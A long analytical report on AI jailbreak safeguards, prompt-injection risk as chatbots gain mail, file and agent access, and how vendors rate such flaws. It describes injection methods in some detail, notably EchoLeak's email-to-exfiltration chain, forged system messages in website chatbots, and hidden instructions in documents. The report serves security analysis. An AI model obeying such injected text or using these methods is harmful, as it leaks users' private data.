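| Design | High-risk jailbreaks found | Attempts | Computing cost relative to the first design | Refusals |
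|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separate input and output classifiers | 13 | 695,000 | 100% | 0.073% |
| Exchange classifier | 2 | 226,000 | 150% | 0.038% |
| Two-stage version | 5 | 569,000 | 27.8% | 0.036% |
| Final version with probe | 1 | 198,000 | 3.5% | 0.050% |

The final system clearly uses less extra computation, which Anthropic puts at about 1%, down from 23.7% in 2025. The size of the improvement in refusals depends on the comparison. Anthropic reports an 87% drop from the 2025 system's refusal rate of 0.38%, but the drop is only about a third when measured against the rebuilt version of the old design in the table, which had a rate of 0.073%.

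The evidence for better protection is weaker. At the first design's rate, 198,000 attempts would have produced about 3.7 high-risk jailbreaks on average. If the attempts were independent, that same rate would produce one or none about 12% of the time by chance. The designs also protected different models, and the researchers changed some of the questions and rewards between tests.

Nobody found a universal jailbreak for the final version in 1,736 hours of attacks. Nobody found one for the two-stage version in its paid test either, but experts outside that programme did, with substantial effort and automated tools. The final version's result may also depend on who the attackers were and what tools they had.

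### The safety margin

According to Anthropic's *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026), the company deliberately sets its classifier to block some requests that are probably harmless along with the harmful ones. It calls the blocked harmless requests a "safety margin", and it made this margin much larger for Fable 5 than for any earlier model.

Most people who ask Fable 5 to look for security flaws in their own code want to fix them, but an attacker could use the same answer. Anthropic uses a classifier to block a large fraction of these low-risk requests, along with more dangerous ones such as requests to write ransomware. A user who disguises a request just enough to get past the classifier will probably get help only with a low-risk task, such as finding a flaw that other tools would also find.

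Anthropic divides jailbreaks into three kinds by how far they get:

- A minor jailbreak gets an answer that lies within the margin and is very unlikely to be harmful.
- A narrow harmful jailbreak unlocks one specific dangerous behaviour.
- A universal jailbreak unlocks a whole class of dangerous behaviours.

The margin helps against weak disguises, which move a request only slightly past the line. It does nothing against a universal jailbreak, because the attacker can ask for the most dangerous content directly. Its value also depends on the vendor's judgement of what is harmless. In June 2026, Amazon researchers reported a technique that got Fable 5 to find several software flaws and write code that exploited one of them. The report led the US government to restrict access to the model. Anthropic still considered the technique minor, arguing that every other model it tested, including its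 much smaller Claude Haiku 4.5, could produce the same exploit.

Anthropic trained a new classifier that stops the Amazon technique in over 99% of cases, but it also blocks harmless requests more often during routine coding and debugging. When it blocks a request, the product tells the user and sends the request to a less capable model, which at the time was Claude Opus 4.8. The user still gets an answer, but it may be worse than the one she is paying for.

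The safeguards disrupted harmless use more in biology. Anthropic's *Improving Fable 5's biology safeguards* (2026) says the company launched the model with almost all biology questions blocked, which affected people who wanted to understand a symptom or a laboratory result. In August it rewrote the classifier's constitution to describe harmless uses in more detail. In its own tests, this sent about 85% fewer biology questions to the weaker model, Claude Opus 5. Questions about virology, toxicology and molecular design still go to Opus 5, so Fable 5 remains unsuitable for professional drug research.

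Much of the original margin in biology apparently came from a classifier that couldn't yet distinguish harmless questions from dangerous ones. Results for Opus 5 suggest the same. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) describes it as no more capable overall than Fable 5. *Claude Opus 5*, by the blogger thezvi, notes that safety classifiers interrupted 5% of one benchmark with the new model, down from 42%, while measures of resistance to attack changed little. Better classifiers may therefore let vendors shrink the margin without making jailbreaks much easier.

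### What testers found on recent models

AISI's *Frontier AI Trends Report*, which covers models released up to October 2025, says the institute found universal jailbreaks in every system it tested. On one model, an expert needed 10 minutes to find and apply a publicly known technique that unlocked answers about biological misuse, but on another model released six months later, experts needed more than seven hours and had to invent a new technique.

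The seven hours are the time an expert needs to discover a jailbreak. AISI expects a novice would take far longer. But anyone who obtains a finished technique can skip the discovery, as the tester did with the first model. The figures also don't show whether the answers were accurate or whether a novice could have used them.

Biology is one of the best-protected subjects. In the talk *State of Jailbreaks*, Davies (2025), a member of AISI, reported that finding a jailbreak took about five hours for biological misuse and 10 minutes for other harmful content. Davies also reported that open-weight models were 15 times easier to compromise than closed ones. Anyone who downloads an open-weight model can train it not to refuse and run it without classifiers, and the developer can't fix copies that people already have.

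Testers continued to break safeguards in 2026. Digital Watch's *GPT-5.5 ranks among strongest models in UK cyber evaluation* reports that AISI's experts found a universal jailbreak for OpenAI's GPT-5.5. The jailbreak produced forbidden content for every malicious cyber request that OpenAI had supplied, including in multi-step tasks.

Fable 5 did better, at least at first. According to Anthropic, testers including AISI, the US government and private organisations spent thousands of hours on its safeguards before its release. By 30 June, three weeks after the launch, nobody had found a universal jailbreak, though Anthropic thinks someone probably will eventually.

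OpenAI reports that GPT-6 Astra, which it released in September 2026, refused 91.5% of requests on the company's cyber jailbreak tests, compared with 59% for the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol. Such comparisons call for caution because, according to OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), its fixed set of jailbreak prompts used attacks that other models had written specifically to defeat earlier GPT models, so those models were bound to do badly. To check that Astra had not simply learned to recognise one attacker's style, OpenAI took half of the prompts from an attacking model that it had not used in training.

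The card's jailbreak tests cover only the model's own refusals, not the classifiers and other safeguards in ChatGPT. An attack that succeeds in the tests might still fail in ChatGPT, so the tests don't show how often a user could get a harmful answer.

OpenAI also tested Astra against attackers that could read its answers and change their approach over several turns. The model passed only if it gave no harmful help in any of a set number of attempts. This is much harder than resisting one attempt. If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of success, the model's chance of resisting all of 100 attempts would be:

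0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 0.37

If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of success, an attacker with 100 tries would succeed at least once about 63% of the time. Real attempts aren't independent, because the attacker learns from each failure. The vendor can also learn from these failures and suspend the account before the hundredth attempt.

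## How the risk grows as tools and integrations are added

Many people connect their chatbot to their mail, files or calendar, and some let it act there without asking first. An instruction that fools the model can then do more harm, although the model is no easier to fool than before.

### One instruction in four set-ups

Suppose a bakery owner receives a price list from a stranger posing as a flour supplier. The list contains a hidden instruction to find her bank details and send them to the stranger.

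If she pastes the list into a bare model, at worst she gets a false summary, perhaps with a fraudulent payment link.

In a default chat, she would probably upload the list as a file. The model could then search its memory and, on some plans, her past chats, where she may have asked for help with a loan application. It would still have to get those details past the vendor's checks on web addresses and sandbox connections, as Claude did in Claudy Day.

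Once a user connects her mailbox and files to a chatbot, an attacker can email her instructions meant for the model. When she asks the chatbot what arrived this morning, the model reads those instructions along with her other mail. Her bank details are probably in an old invoice, even if she has never mentioned them to the chatbot. If the model can also send email, it can send them to the attacker directly instead of through a hidden channel, and the only remaining safeguard may be her approval of each message.

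An agent that acts without approval removes that obstacle too. It can forward the invoice with a function she deliberately gave it. McKerchar, writing for the security company Sophos, notes that an agent follows injected instructions "with the user's privileges". The mail server receives a valid request from her account and has no reason to refuse it. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) similarly warns companies that a valid credential may give an agent access to a system without settling which actions it is authorised to take there.

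The table shows what the stranger could achieve in each set-up if the model obeyed. Each row adds to the one above it.

| Set-up | What it can read | Where hostile text can enter | What it can send or change | Whether the harm can be undone |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bare model | The conversation | Text the user pastes in | Its own answer | Yes, if she hasn't acted on the answer |
| Default chat | Memory, uploaded files and, on some plans, past chats | Files, web pages, search results and pre-filled links | Web requests and saved memories | She can delete a false memory but can't recall leaked data |
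| Chat connected to mail and files | The mailbox and stored documents | Any incoming email or shared document | Messages and edits that she approves | She can reverse an edit if an older version exists, but not a sent email |
| Agent that acts without approval | Everything its accounts can open | Anything it comes across during a task | Messages, deletions and purchases, with nobody checking | Deleted files need a backup, and a payment may be gone for good |

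### More ways in, more data and more actions

A new connection can give strangers another way to reach the model, give the model access to more private data, or let it take more actions. It doesn't always do all three. For example, a folder of old tax returns mainly adds private data, while a tool that reads customer reviews mainly adds text from strangers.

To steal data, an attacker needs an entry point, a data store and a way out, so the number of possible combinations is the number of each multiplied together. A product with three entry points, four data stores and two ways out has 3 × 4 × 2 = 24 combinations. Adding one of each raises the total to 4 × 5 × 3 = 60. Many combinations won't work in practice, but the vendor has to consider all of them.

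Even simple chatbots on ordinary websites have these problems. *When AI Meets the Web* examined 17 plugins that website owners use to add a chatbot built on a commercial model. The researchers found the plugins on 10,417 websites in a public web archive from August 2024, and on 17,474 by April 2025. Of the 200 sites the researchers visited, 125 had a working chatbot.

Eight of the plugins, used by about 8,000 sites, sent the conversation history from the visitor's browser with every new message and didn't check whether the visitor had altered it. Visitors could therefore invent earlier answers from the chatbot and, in seven of the eight plugins, add fake system messages, which the model treated as the site owner's instructions. Forged histories made the chatbot three to eight times as likely to behave in unintended ways, such as writing computer code for a visitor at the owner's expense.

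Fifteen plugins could copy a website's text into the chatbot's knowledge base without separating the owner's product descriptions from customers' reviews. An attacker could post a review containing instructions, and the chatbot might follow them when a later customer asked about the product. To see how many shops were exposed, the researchers randomly picked 100 that used the most popular plugin and had working chatbots. They asked the chatbots about particular customers' complaints, and 13 gave details that came from reviews.

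The 13% is the share of shops where an attacker's text could reach the model. The researchers planted nothing on these sites, so they did not measure how often an attack would succeed. With a sample of 100, the true share among shops using that plugin could be from about 8% to 21%. The method may also have missed some of these shops, because several chatbots refused to discuss customers.

Seven plugins increased the risk by inserting the copied text as a system message. In a simulated shop with a loosely worded system prompt, five OpenAI models followed a planted instruction in 38% of trials when it arrived as a system message and in 8% as tool output. Role tags evidently give some protection, even though Ye and colleagues found that a text's wording affects the model more than its role tag does.

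The researchers also gave a simulated website chatbot a tool for posting notices to Slack, a workplace messaging service, and tried to make it post a malicious link in a channel that the whole company could read. Three of Google's Gemini models posted the link in every trial when the instruction came in an ordinary visitor's message.

A stricter system prompt didn't prevent this. The table shows how often each of the five OpenAI models obeyed a forged system message in ten trials.

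| The owner's system prompt | Wrote code for the visitor | Posted the link to Slack |
|---|---|---|
| Loosely worded | 98% | 30% |
| Forbids tasks outside the chatbot's role | 62% | 40% |
| Also forbids coding | 24% | 60% |

The rise in the last column may not mean much, because there were so few trials and the models differed widely. But a prompt that kept a chatbot to its job clearly did little to protect its tools. The models date from 2025 or earlier, so newer ones may do better. Even so, owners were quick to add tools. Two months after the most popular plugin introduced them, the researchers found 144 chatbots with tools switched on.

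### EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Microsoft 365 Copilot, the business version of Copilot, answers employees' questions from their company's mail and files. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs told Microsoft that an outsider could steal this data with an email. Reddy and Gujral, in *EchoLeak*, describe the flaw as a chain of bypasses that needed only "a single crafted email". The attack worked as follows:

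1. The attacker emails an employee. Microsoft used a classifier to detect instructions hidden in outside content, but the attacker's email got past it.
2. The email stays in the mailbox until the employee asks Copilot a question. Copilot searches for relevant passages and adds them to the context, a method called retrieval-augmented generation (RAG). The attacker can make the email long and cover many subjects in it, or send several emails, so that some passage matches whatever the employee asks. Aim Labs called this "RAG spraying".
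3. The context now contains the attacker's instructions next to the company's own information. The model picks out the most sensitive information and writes it into a web address in its answer.
4. Copilot had a safeguard that removed links from answers, but the attack got around it.
5. The address carries the data to the attacker's server.

*Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Willison, 2025) describes the last step as a Markdown link that leaks the data when the user clicks it. Aim Labs reported that the attack needed no click. This would be possible if the link were an image address, because a chat window requests images automatically. The employee still had to ask Copilot a question, but it could be any question that matched the email.

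Willison considers EchoLeak an extended version of attacks already seen in "a dozen different products". Copilot's access to the mailbox made the attack more dangerous, because the attacker only needed an employee's email address and didn't have to persuade her to open a file or follow a link. Copilot only answered a question and didn't send an email or change a file, so a company can't rule out this kind of theft by making its assistant read-only.

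Windows Central's *Microsoft Copilot's own default configuration exposed users* points out that the attack worked on Copilot's default settings. By default, Copilot can access company data that a ChatGPT or Claude user would have to connect. Microsoft finished its patch in May 2025, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, and Aim Labs published its findings on 11 June. The Hacker News' *Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Exposes Microsoft 365 Copilot Data Without User Interaction* reports no evidence that anyone exploited the flaw maliciously.

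### Why repeated attempts matter

Connecting a chatbot to a mailbox also gives attackers more chances. In a default chat, they get one only when the victim opens something they wrote or asks a question that leads to their page. Once a mailbox is connected, they can send the assistant a new email every day or write to every employee in a company.

If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in *k* attempts is:

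1 − (1 − *p*)ᵏ

With *p* = 1%, the chance is about 63% after 100 attempts, as in the jailbreak example above, and 99% after 500.

Real attempts aren't independent, partly because some targets are much weaker than others. Suppose an attack works 10% of the time on one company's assistant and never on those of nine others. The average success rate is 1%, and the formula predicts that 100 attempts on each company will breach about six of the ten. The attacker will almost certainly breach the weak one and none of the others. When targets differ this much, the average rate overstates how many will be breached and understates the risk to the weakest.

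The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that strong attacks on this model, released in November 2025, succeeded 4.7% of the time on the first attempt and 63% of the time within 100 attempts. If the attempts had been independent, the success rate within 100 would have been 99%.

Attempts also affect one another because, as with jailbreaks, both the attacker and the vendor can learn from each failure.

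### Injection rates in coding, computer and browser use

Anthropic's July 2026 system card for Claude Opus 5 gives injection rates for three kinds of work. In the coding tests, the attacker planted instructions in material the model read while programming. In the computer-use tests, the model operated a graphical interface, and in the browser tests, it worked with web pages in Claude Cowork. The table shows the results with extended reasoning on. The fourth column uses the formula above.

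| Use | Attempts per scenario | Successful attempts | Scenarios expected to fall if attempts were independent | Scenarios that fell | Scenarios that fell with added safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | 200 | 0.56% | 27 of 40 | 13 of 40 | 4 of 40 |
| Computer use | 200 | 0.54% | 9 of 14 | 1 of 14 | 1 of 14 |
| Browser | 10 | 3.70% | 41 of 129 | 11 of 129 | 0 of 129 |

In computer use, attacks succeeded in only one of the 14 scenarios, where about 15 of 200 attempts worked, or roughly 8%. The overall success rate of 0.54% averages that scenario with 13 in which every attack failed, so it is a poor estimate of the risk in any single scenario.

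The rows aren't directly comparable, because Anthropic used a different attacker for each. It developed the coding attacks against earlier models before trying them on Opus 5, whereas it optimised the computer-use attacks directly on the test scenarios. Professional testers wrote the browser attacks, and Anthropic chose scenarios in which the model was certain to see them. Anthropic also used different safeguards. In coding and computer use, it added probes that inspect tool output before the model acts on it, and in the browser it also added a classifier that can block dangerous actions. The higher success rate in the browser therefore doesn't prove that browsing is the riskiest use.

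A model that resists prompt injection in one kind of work can be weak in another. Claude Mythos 5 did slightly better than Opus 5 in coding, where 0.45% of attacks succeeded, but 29.7% succeeded against it in the browser. VentureBeat reported a similar gap for Claude Opus 4.6 in February 2026. In a coding test, none of 200 attempts succeeded, but in a graphical interface the attacker had a 78.6% chance of success within 200 attempts, or 57.1% with safeguards on.

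The card has no figure for an ordinary chat. The nearest measurement is in *The Framing Gap*, which reported no leaks in 48 trials of ChatGPT, but those trials used different attacks on another vendor's product. Without a chat figure from the same tests, this evidence does not show how much more often an injection succeeds once a chatbot becomes an agent. The case that integrations increase risk therefore depends mainly on what a successful injection can reach and do.

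The card also compares vendors on 1,130 attacks that Anthropic, other developers and two government institutes built with the security company Gray Swan. The attacks are meant to cause harm that is hard to reverse, such as data theft, deleted data and unwanted payments. An attacker with 15 attempts had a 2.0% chance of success against Opus 5 and 20.0% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic tested its own models without extra safeguards and the others through their public services, which may have had some, so the test setup does not obviously favour Claude.

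The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* bases its headline on a result of 0 failures in 129 scenarios, and contrasts it with OpenAI's admission in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved. The result is a large improvement, but it applies to one product with its strongest safeguards on. The model alone failed in 11 of the scenarios. Even with the safeguards, the failure rate on similar scenarios could still be about 2%, because 129 is a small sample.

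According to its system card, Claude Opus 5.5, released in September, performed about as well as Opus 5 or better on every injection test Anthropic reports. Anthropic announced a further release on 9 November in *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026).

### Meta's Rule of Two

If a model can't reliably resist injection, a developer can still limit what a successful one achieves. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) offers a simple rule for this. Conffab's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), which summarises it, lists three properties, of which an agent should have no more than two in any session:

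- It processes untrustworthy inputs.
- It has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change something or communicate with the outside world.

Meta's rule builds on Willison's three conditions for data theft. His third condition covers only sending data out, but Meta's third property also covers harm such as deleting files or buying things. Meta intends the rule to apply until developers can reliably detect and refuse injected instructions. A second summary, also titled *Agents Rule of Two*, adds that a person must approve the agent's actions if a task needs all three properties.

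Meta's example is Email-Bot, an assistant that reads new mail from anyone, searches the existing inbox and sends replies, so it has all three properties. Its developer could let it read only mail from known colleagues, deny it access to older messages, or have it write drafts for the user to send. Each change makes the assistant safer but less useful, because people want it to handle strangers' messages, use older ones and send replies. This is the main practical objection to the rule.

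If an agent asks for approval before every reply, users may learn to click through the requests, as OpenAI feared they would with link warnings. Approval helps only if the screen shows what the agent is about to send and to whom.

The rule can also make an agent look safer than it is. Meta's diagram labels every pair of properties "safe", but the website chatbot that posted a malicious link to Slack needed only a stranger's message and the ability to post, without any private data. A company's Slack is arguably a sensitive system itself, which would give the chatbot all three properties. Developers therefore have to decide what counts as sensitive before they can apply the rule, and those who decide wrongly will believe the agent is safe.

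Memory complicates the rule, which applies to one session at a time. On Monday, an agent with no access to private data might read a hostile web page and save a note containing an instruction from it. On Tuesday, it opens the user's files, with no web access but with permission to send email. If the developer counts the note as trusted, each session has only two of the rule's properties, even though the instruction came from a stranger, as in Rehberger's attacks on ChatGPT's memory. To apply the rule properly, a developer would have to treat anything saved while reading untrusted text as untrusted.

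Default chatbots don't follow the rule either. A session with memory and web access has all three properties before the user connects anything, and Claude doesn't ask permission each time it fetches a page. Vendors instead narrow the third property, for instance by restricting which addresses the model can open.

### When a default chat holds more than an agent

An agent may not always be riskier than a default chat, though the four set-ups seem to suggest it is. Someone who has talked to a chatbot for years may have told it about her health, her marriage and her debts. An agent that only sorts a company's invoices has none of this information, even if it acts without approval. Claudy Day also showed that an attacker could steal a message about a user's health from a session with no integrations.

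The objection is right about the data. The order of the set-ups applies to one product as its user adds connections, not to comparisons between different products. If an agent sorts invoices into folders and can't contact anyone outside the company, an injection may at worst make it misfile them. The company can correct that, but a user of the default chat can't undo the disclosure of her diagnosis to a stranger.

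Whether a default chat or a connected one is riskier depends on more than how much data each holds. An attacker has fewer ways to get text into a default chat and data out of it. An agent that reads every incoming invoice and can pay them has little private data but could lose a large sum in one step.

The risk is greatest when the same assistant has both a long memory and broad permissions. If the baker connects her mailbox to a chatbot that has her loan application in memory, one hostile email could expose both. A separate mail agent with no memory of her chats would expose only the mailbox.

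## How vendors rate prompt injection and data leaks

When a researcher reports a prompt injection, the vendor has to decide whether it is a security flaw, how urgently to fix it and whether to pay for the report. Microsoft publishes severity ratings for flaws in AI systems. Google, OpenAI and Anthropic publish the terms of their bug bounties. All four companies look mainly at what the attacker achieved. They usually treat an injection as a security flaw if the attacker used it to steal someone's data, but usually not if it only changed an answer.

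### Microsoft's severity table

An attacker who controls part of a model's input can manipulate its output, but only some manipulations affect security (Microsoft, 2025). Microsoft therefore rates an injection by its effect and by how much the victim has to do. Its classification also covers some leaks that need no injection. The table shows the ratings most relevant to chatbots.

| What the attacker achieves | Severity |
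|---|---|
| Steals another user's data, or performs privileged actions on that user's behalf, with no user interaction | Critical |
| Does the same with some user interaction, such as a click | Important |
| Only influences the model's output | No severity; "content-related issue" |
| Extracts another user's confidential input | Important |
| Extracts another user's input that is not confidential | Low |
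| Reconstructs a confidential record from the training data | Important |
| Reconstructs a public record from the training data | Low |

Microsoft assesses content-related issues separately, under its principles for responsible AI. *Updating our Vulnerability Severity Classification for AI Systems*, which announced the classification in 2023, rated a manipulated answer as more severe if other users saw it or if it affected decisions about them. But under the current table, an attack that uses a web page to make Copilot give someone a false answer has no severity unless the attacker also steals data or acts on the user's behalf.

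An attack on a plain chat can still get a high rating, because the table doesn't require the user to have connected anything to it. *Reprompt*, the attack on Copilot Personal, stole chat details after one click, so it fits the description of an Important flaw. The planted memory in *CoSnitch* is harder to rate. It made Copilot describe a known software flaw as harmless, which only influences output, but Microsoft could also regard writing to a user's Copilot memory as a "privileged action", a term the table doesn't define.

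It is also unclear how much a victim has to do before Microsoft counts it as interaction. EchoLeak worked only after an employee asked Copilot a question, yet Microsoft rated it Critical. Microsoft apparently doesn't count ordinary use of the product as interaction if the victim never has to click anything.

The rating for leaked training data depends on how confidential the record was. Most of what Nasr and colleagues could verify in ChatGPT's output matched public web pages, so it would probably rate Low on Microsoft's scale, even if a page contained someone's telephone number. Whisper Leak, which identifies a chat's topic from encrypted traffic, falls outside these categories because they cover only information that an attacker infers by using the model. Microsoft rates other leaks under its older rules.

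### Google's rewards

On 6 October 2025, Google opened a separate reward programme for flaws in its AI products. Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Launches AI Bug Bounty with $30,000 Top Reward* reports that the programme covers flaws to which interaction with a generative AI system is integral. Researchers must verify the flaw and explain the threat in plain language.

Google sorts these flaws into eight categories, which TechRadar's *Google launches AI bug bounties* lists as S1, S2 and A1 to A6. The table shows the categories for which press reports give a maximum reward. The three lowest amounts come from Particle.news' *Google Launches Dedicated AI Bug Bounty With Rewards Up to $30,000*, and the others come from SecurityWeek's *Google Offers Up to $20,000 in New AI Bug Bounty Program*.

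| Category | What the attack does | Highest base reward |
|---|---|---|
| Rogue actions | Changes the victim's account or data, with a clear effect on security | $20,000 |
| Sensitive data exfiltration | Leaks private information without the user's approval | $15,000 |
| Phishing enablement | Plants lasting, convincing web content on a Google site where other users see it without a warning | $5,000 |
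| Model theft | Extracts a model's parameters | $5,000 |
| Context manipulation | Makes a lasting change to the victim's AI environment without much interaction | $5,000 |

The other categories are unauthorised access to data, unauthorised use of server features and persistent denial of service. Google pays the most for flaws in its flagship products, which include Gemini, Search and the main Workspace applications such as Gmail. Bonuses for novelty and a well-written report can raise a $20,000 reward to $30,000.

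Press reports differ on whether Google pays for reports of prompt injection. SecurityWeek and Infosecurity Magazine list it as out of scope, along with jailbreaks, while TechRadar includes it among the vulnerabilities covered. Google probably doesn't exclude every injection, because it pays for reports of chatbots leaking another person's data, and injection is the usual way to cause such leaks. The exclusion makes most sense for direct injection, in which a user manipulates their own session, and for injections that only change what the model writes.

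Google's reason is that a reward programme isn't suited to problems with a model's content. Kotsovinos and Flynn (2025), in *How we're securing the AI frontier*, ask people to report these problems through the product's feedback function. The function records details such as the model version and the user's context, which Google's safety teams need to diagnose the behaviour and retrain the model.

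An attack on an ordinary Gemini chat can therefore qualify. A researcher could earn up to $15,000 for an attack that sends a user's private messages to an attacker. An injection that plants a false memory might count as context manipulation, which *Google will pay you up to $30,000 in rewards to find bugs* defines as persistent and requiring no "significant user interaction". ChatGPhish, the fake security warning in a summary, would probably earn nothing if it worked on Gemini. Google's phishing category requires lasting content that other users see, but the warning appears only in one user's answer.

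### OpenAI's and Anthropic's rules

OpenAI (2026) opened a Safety Bug Bounty on 25 March for problems that may not meet its definition of a security vulnerability. It accepts third-party prompt injection if, at least 50% of the time, the attacker's text takes over a victim's agent and makes it do something harmful or leak sensitive information. OpenAI names its browser, ChatGPT Agent and "similar agentic products" as targets.

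Ordinary ChatGPT isn't on that list. A researcher could argue that it is similar to the listed products because it can search the web, run code and save memories, but OpenAI doesn't explain how it distinguishes them. A report about ordinary ChatGPT could also qualify in two other ways. OpenAI considers flaws outside its categories case by case if they lead directly to user harm and have a specific remedy. It also runs an older Security Bug Bounty for conventional flaws, and its staff can move reports between the two programmes. Check Point's use of domain-name lookups to get data out of ChatGPT's sandbox seems to exploit a conventional flaw, because OpenAI could close that route without retraining the model.

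Anthropic's rules have no special category for prompt injection. Its *Responsible Disclosure Policy* (2025) covers technical flaws such as misconfigurations, but excludes adversarial testing of its models and problems with the content of prompts and responses. In May 2026, Anthropic closed its separate disclosure programme to new reports and directed researchers to its bug bounty.

The bounty policy of 7 May does not mention prompt injection by name and still excludes model content. Anthropic eventually accepted Rehberger's report about file uploads, which is better evidence that an injection in an ordinary Claude chat can qualify for a bounty.

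Anthropic also requires such reports to include a working demonstration. It normally wants one flaw per report, but lets researchers combine several when showing the harm requires it. It excludes social engineering, including phishing. A reviewer might apply that exclusion to a misleading advert or link, although the flaw that the link exploits could still count.

### How Claudy Day would rate

In the Claudy Day attack, a crafted link made Claude upload a private message to a stranger's account. The table shows how differently the vendors' schemes would rate it. These ratings are inferences from the published rules, not decisions by the vendors. The ratings for Microsoft, Google and OpenAI assume that the same attack worked on their own chatbots.

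| Scheme | Probable result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft | Important | The attacker steals another user's data, but the victim must follow a link and press Enter |
| Google | Sensitive data exfiltration, up to $15,000 | Private data leaves a flagship product without the user's approval |
| OpenAI | Uncertain | A default chat may not count as an agentic product, though the flaws had specific remedies |
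| Anthropic | In scope, severity unknown | Anthropic accepted Rehberger's similar report, but its policy sets no severity levels for injection |

OpenAI's answer would depend on whether it classified the chatbot as an agent. If it did, the attack would also have to pass the 50% test. Luz claims that the attack works consistently, so it would probably pass.

### A CVSS score for stolen chats

Many companies rate software flaws from 0 to 10 using the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS). FIRST, a non-profit association of security response teams, maintains it. The current version is 4.0, but many advisories still use 3.1. Barlow (2026) argues in *Beyond CVSS* that the system suits many attacks on AI products. In her example, an injected instruction makes a shop's chatbot look up another customer's order. CVSS can score the resulting loss of confidential data like any other leak.

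In version 3.1, an analyst chooses a value for each of eight metrics, and most values have a numerical weight. The table shows reasonable choices for an attack that steals a chat over the internet and does nothing else.

| Metric | Value | Weight |
|---|---|---|
| Attack vector | Network: the attacker can be anywhere on the internet | 0.85 |
| Attack complexity | Low: the attack needs no unusual conditions | 0.77 |
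| Privileges required | None: the attacker has no access to the victim's account | 0.85 |
| User interaction | Required, or None | 0.62, or 0.85 |
| Confidentiality | High: the stolen data is seriously harmful to disclose | 0.56 |
| Integrity | None: the attacker alters nothing | 0 |
| Availability | None: the product keeps working | 0 |

The eighth metric, scope, has no weight of its own but changes the formula. Scope is "unchanged" if the harm stays within the system that contains the flaw, and "changed" if it reaches a system under separate control.

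The score combines how easy the attack is with how much harm it does. Ease of attack, which CVSS calls exploitability, is:

8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.62 ≈ 2.835 with user interaction

8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.85 ≈ 3.887 without it

The impact is:

6.42 × 0.56 ≈ 3.595 with unchanged scope

7.52 × (0.56 − 0.029) − 3.25 × (0.56 − 0.02)¹⁵ ≈ 3.993 with changed scope

CVSS adds the two numbers, multiplies the sum by 1.08 if the scope has changed, and rounds up to the next tenth.

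| User interaction | Scope | Calculation | Score | Severity |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Required | Unchanged | 3.595 + 2.835 = 6.430 | 6.5 | Medium |
| None | Unchanged | 3.595 + 3.887 = 7.482 | 7.5 | High |
| Required | Changed | 1.08 × (3.993 + 2.835) ≈ 7.374 | 7.4 | High |

Claudy Day scores 6.5 on CVSS if the analyst treats Claude and its stored chats as one system, but 7.4, which is rated High, if the analyst treats the chat history as a separate system. Careful analysts could disagree about which is right because CVSS was designed for software with clearer boundaries than a chatbot's.

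### Attacks that work only some of the time

CVSS has no metric for how often an attack succeeds. The closest is attack complexity, which can only be Low or High. Changing it to High would lower Claudy Day's score from 6.5 to 5.3, whether the attack worked on 40% of victims or 1%.

A low success rate also makes a report hard to confirm. Google's *Celebrating One Year of AI Bug Bounties at Alphabet* explains that the same input may produce different answers even when the model and settings are identical. If an attack fails in a test, Google's staff can't tell whether they made a mistake, the report is wrong, or the attack works about once in a hundred tries. A flaw can disappear and return as Google retunes the model. In the first year of rewards for generative AI, Google received over 140 reports, and about one in six led a product team to make a change. That is similar to the rate across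 its other programmes, so the difficulty of reproducing attacks evidently didn't make AI reports much less useful overall.

If an attack has a 1% chance of working on each independent attempt, a reviewer who tries it ten times has a 90% chance of seeing only failures (0.99¹⁰ ≈ 0.90). She would need about 300 attempts for a 95% chance of seeing it work at least once, while an attacker can make more attempts by sending it to more people.

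OpenAI's 50% rule gives researchers a clear target and saves its staff from investigating rare results, but it excludes attacks that would be dangerous on a large scale. An attack that worked 8% of the time, as in the one computer-use scenario where Claude Opus 5 was compromised, would miss the threshold. It would still succeed about 80 times if an attacker sent it to 1,000 similar users.

The number of tests also matters, and OpenAI's announcement doesn't specify one. If an attack's true success rate is 60%, about one in six sets of ten attempts will still have more failures than successes. Researchers can reduce this risk by making many attempts and reporting how many failed, but few published reports of attacks on chatbots include this information.

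### Harm that depends on the user

These schemes are also poorly suited to rating harm that depends on what the user has connected. Microsoft's table could rate a theft from the bakery owner Important both before and after she connected her mailbox. CVSS could give both thefts the maximum value for lost confidentiality, though connecting the mailbox might count as a change of scope, which would raise the score from 6.5 to 7.4. Google adjusts its rewards for the product that has the flaw, but its tiers don't account for what a particular user has connected.

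CVSS lets an organisation adjust a score for its own circumstances, such as storing medical records. This is practical for a company that runs one known system, but the vendor of a consumer chatbot has to choose one priority for millions of users with different memories and connections.

Barlow considers these adjustments insufficient for harm to people or reputations. A hateful answer from a chatbot that promotes a children's book could be a disaster for the publisher, but the same words on an internal page would matter much less. Neither case involves a loss of confidential data, so CVSS has little to measure. She recommends that each company define its own worst outcomes and base severity on those. Her employer, the bug bounty platform Intigriti, sells help with this, but the limitation she describes is real and applies to ChatGPhish, which steals nothing from the chat but could still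 lead a user to give away a password.

### Several minor flaws in one attack

A reviewer who scores flaws separately can underestimate what they do together. Claudy Day began with an open redirect on Anthropic's website. If the redirect caused only a small loss of integrity, it would score 4.3 under CVSS. Hidden text in a pre-filled prompt might score about the same, since on its own it might only change Claude's answer. Both would look less urgent than a flaw that exposed data directly, but together they brought an attacker's instructions into a victim's chat. The third flaw, the upload to a stranger's account, was also easy to misjudge on its own, as Anthropic's first response to Rehberger had shown.

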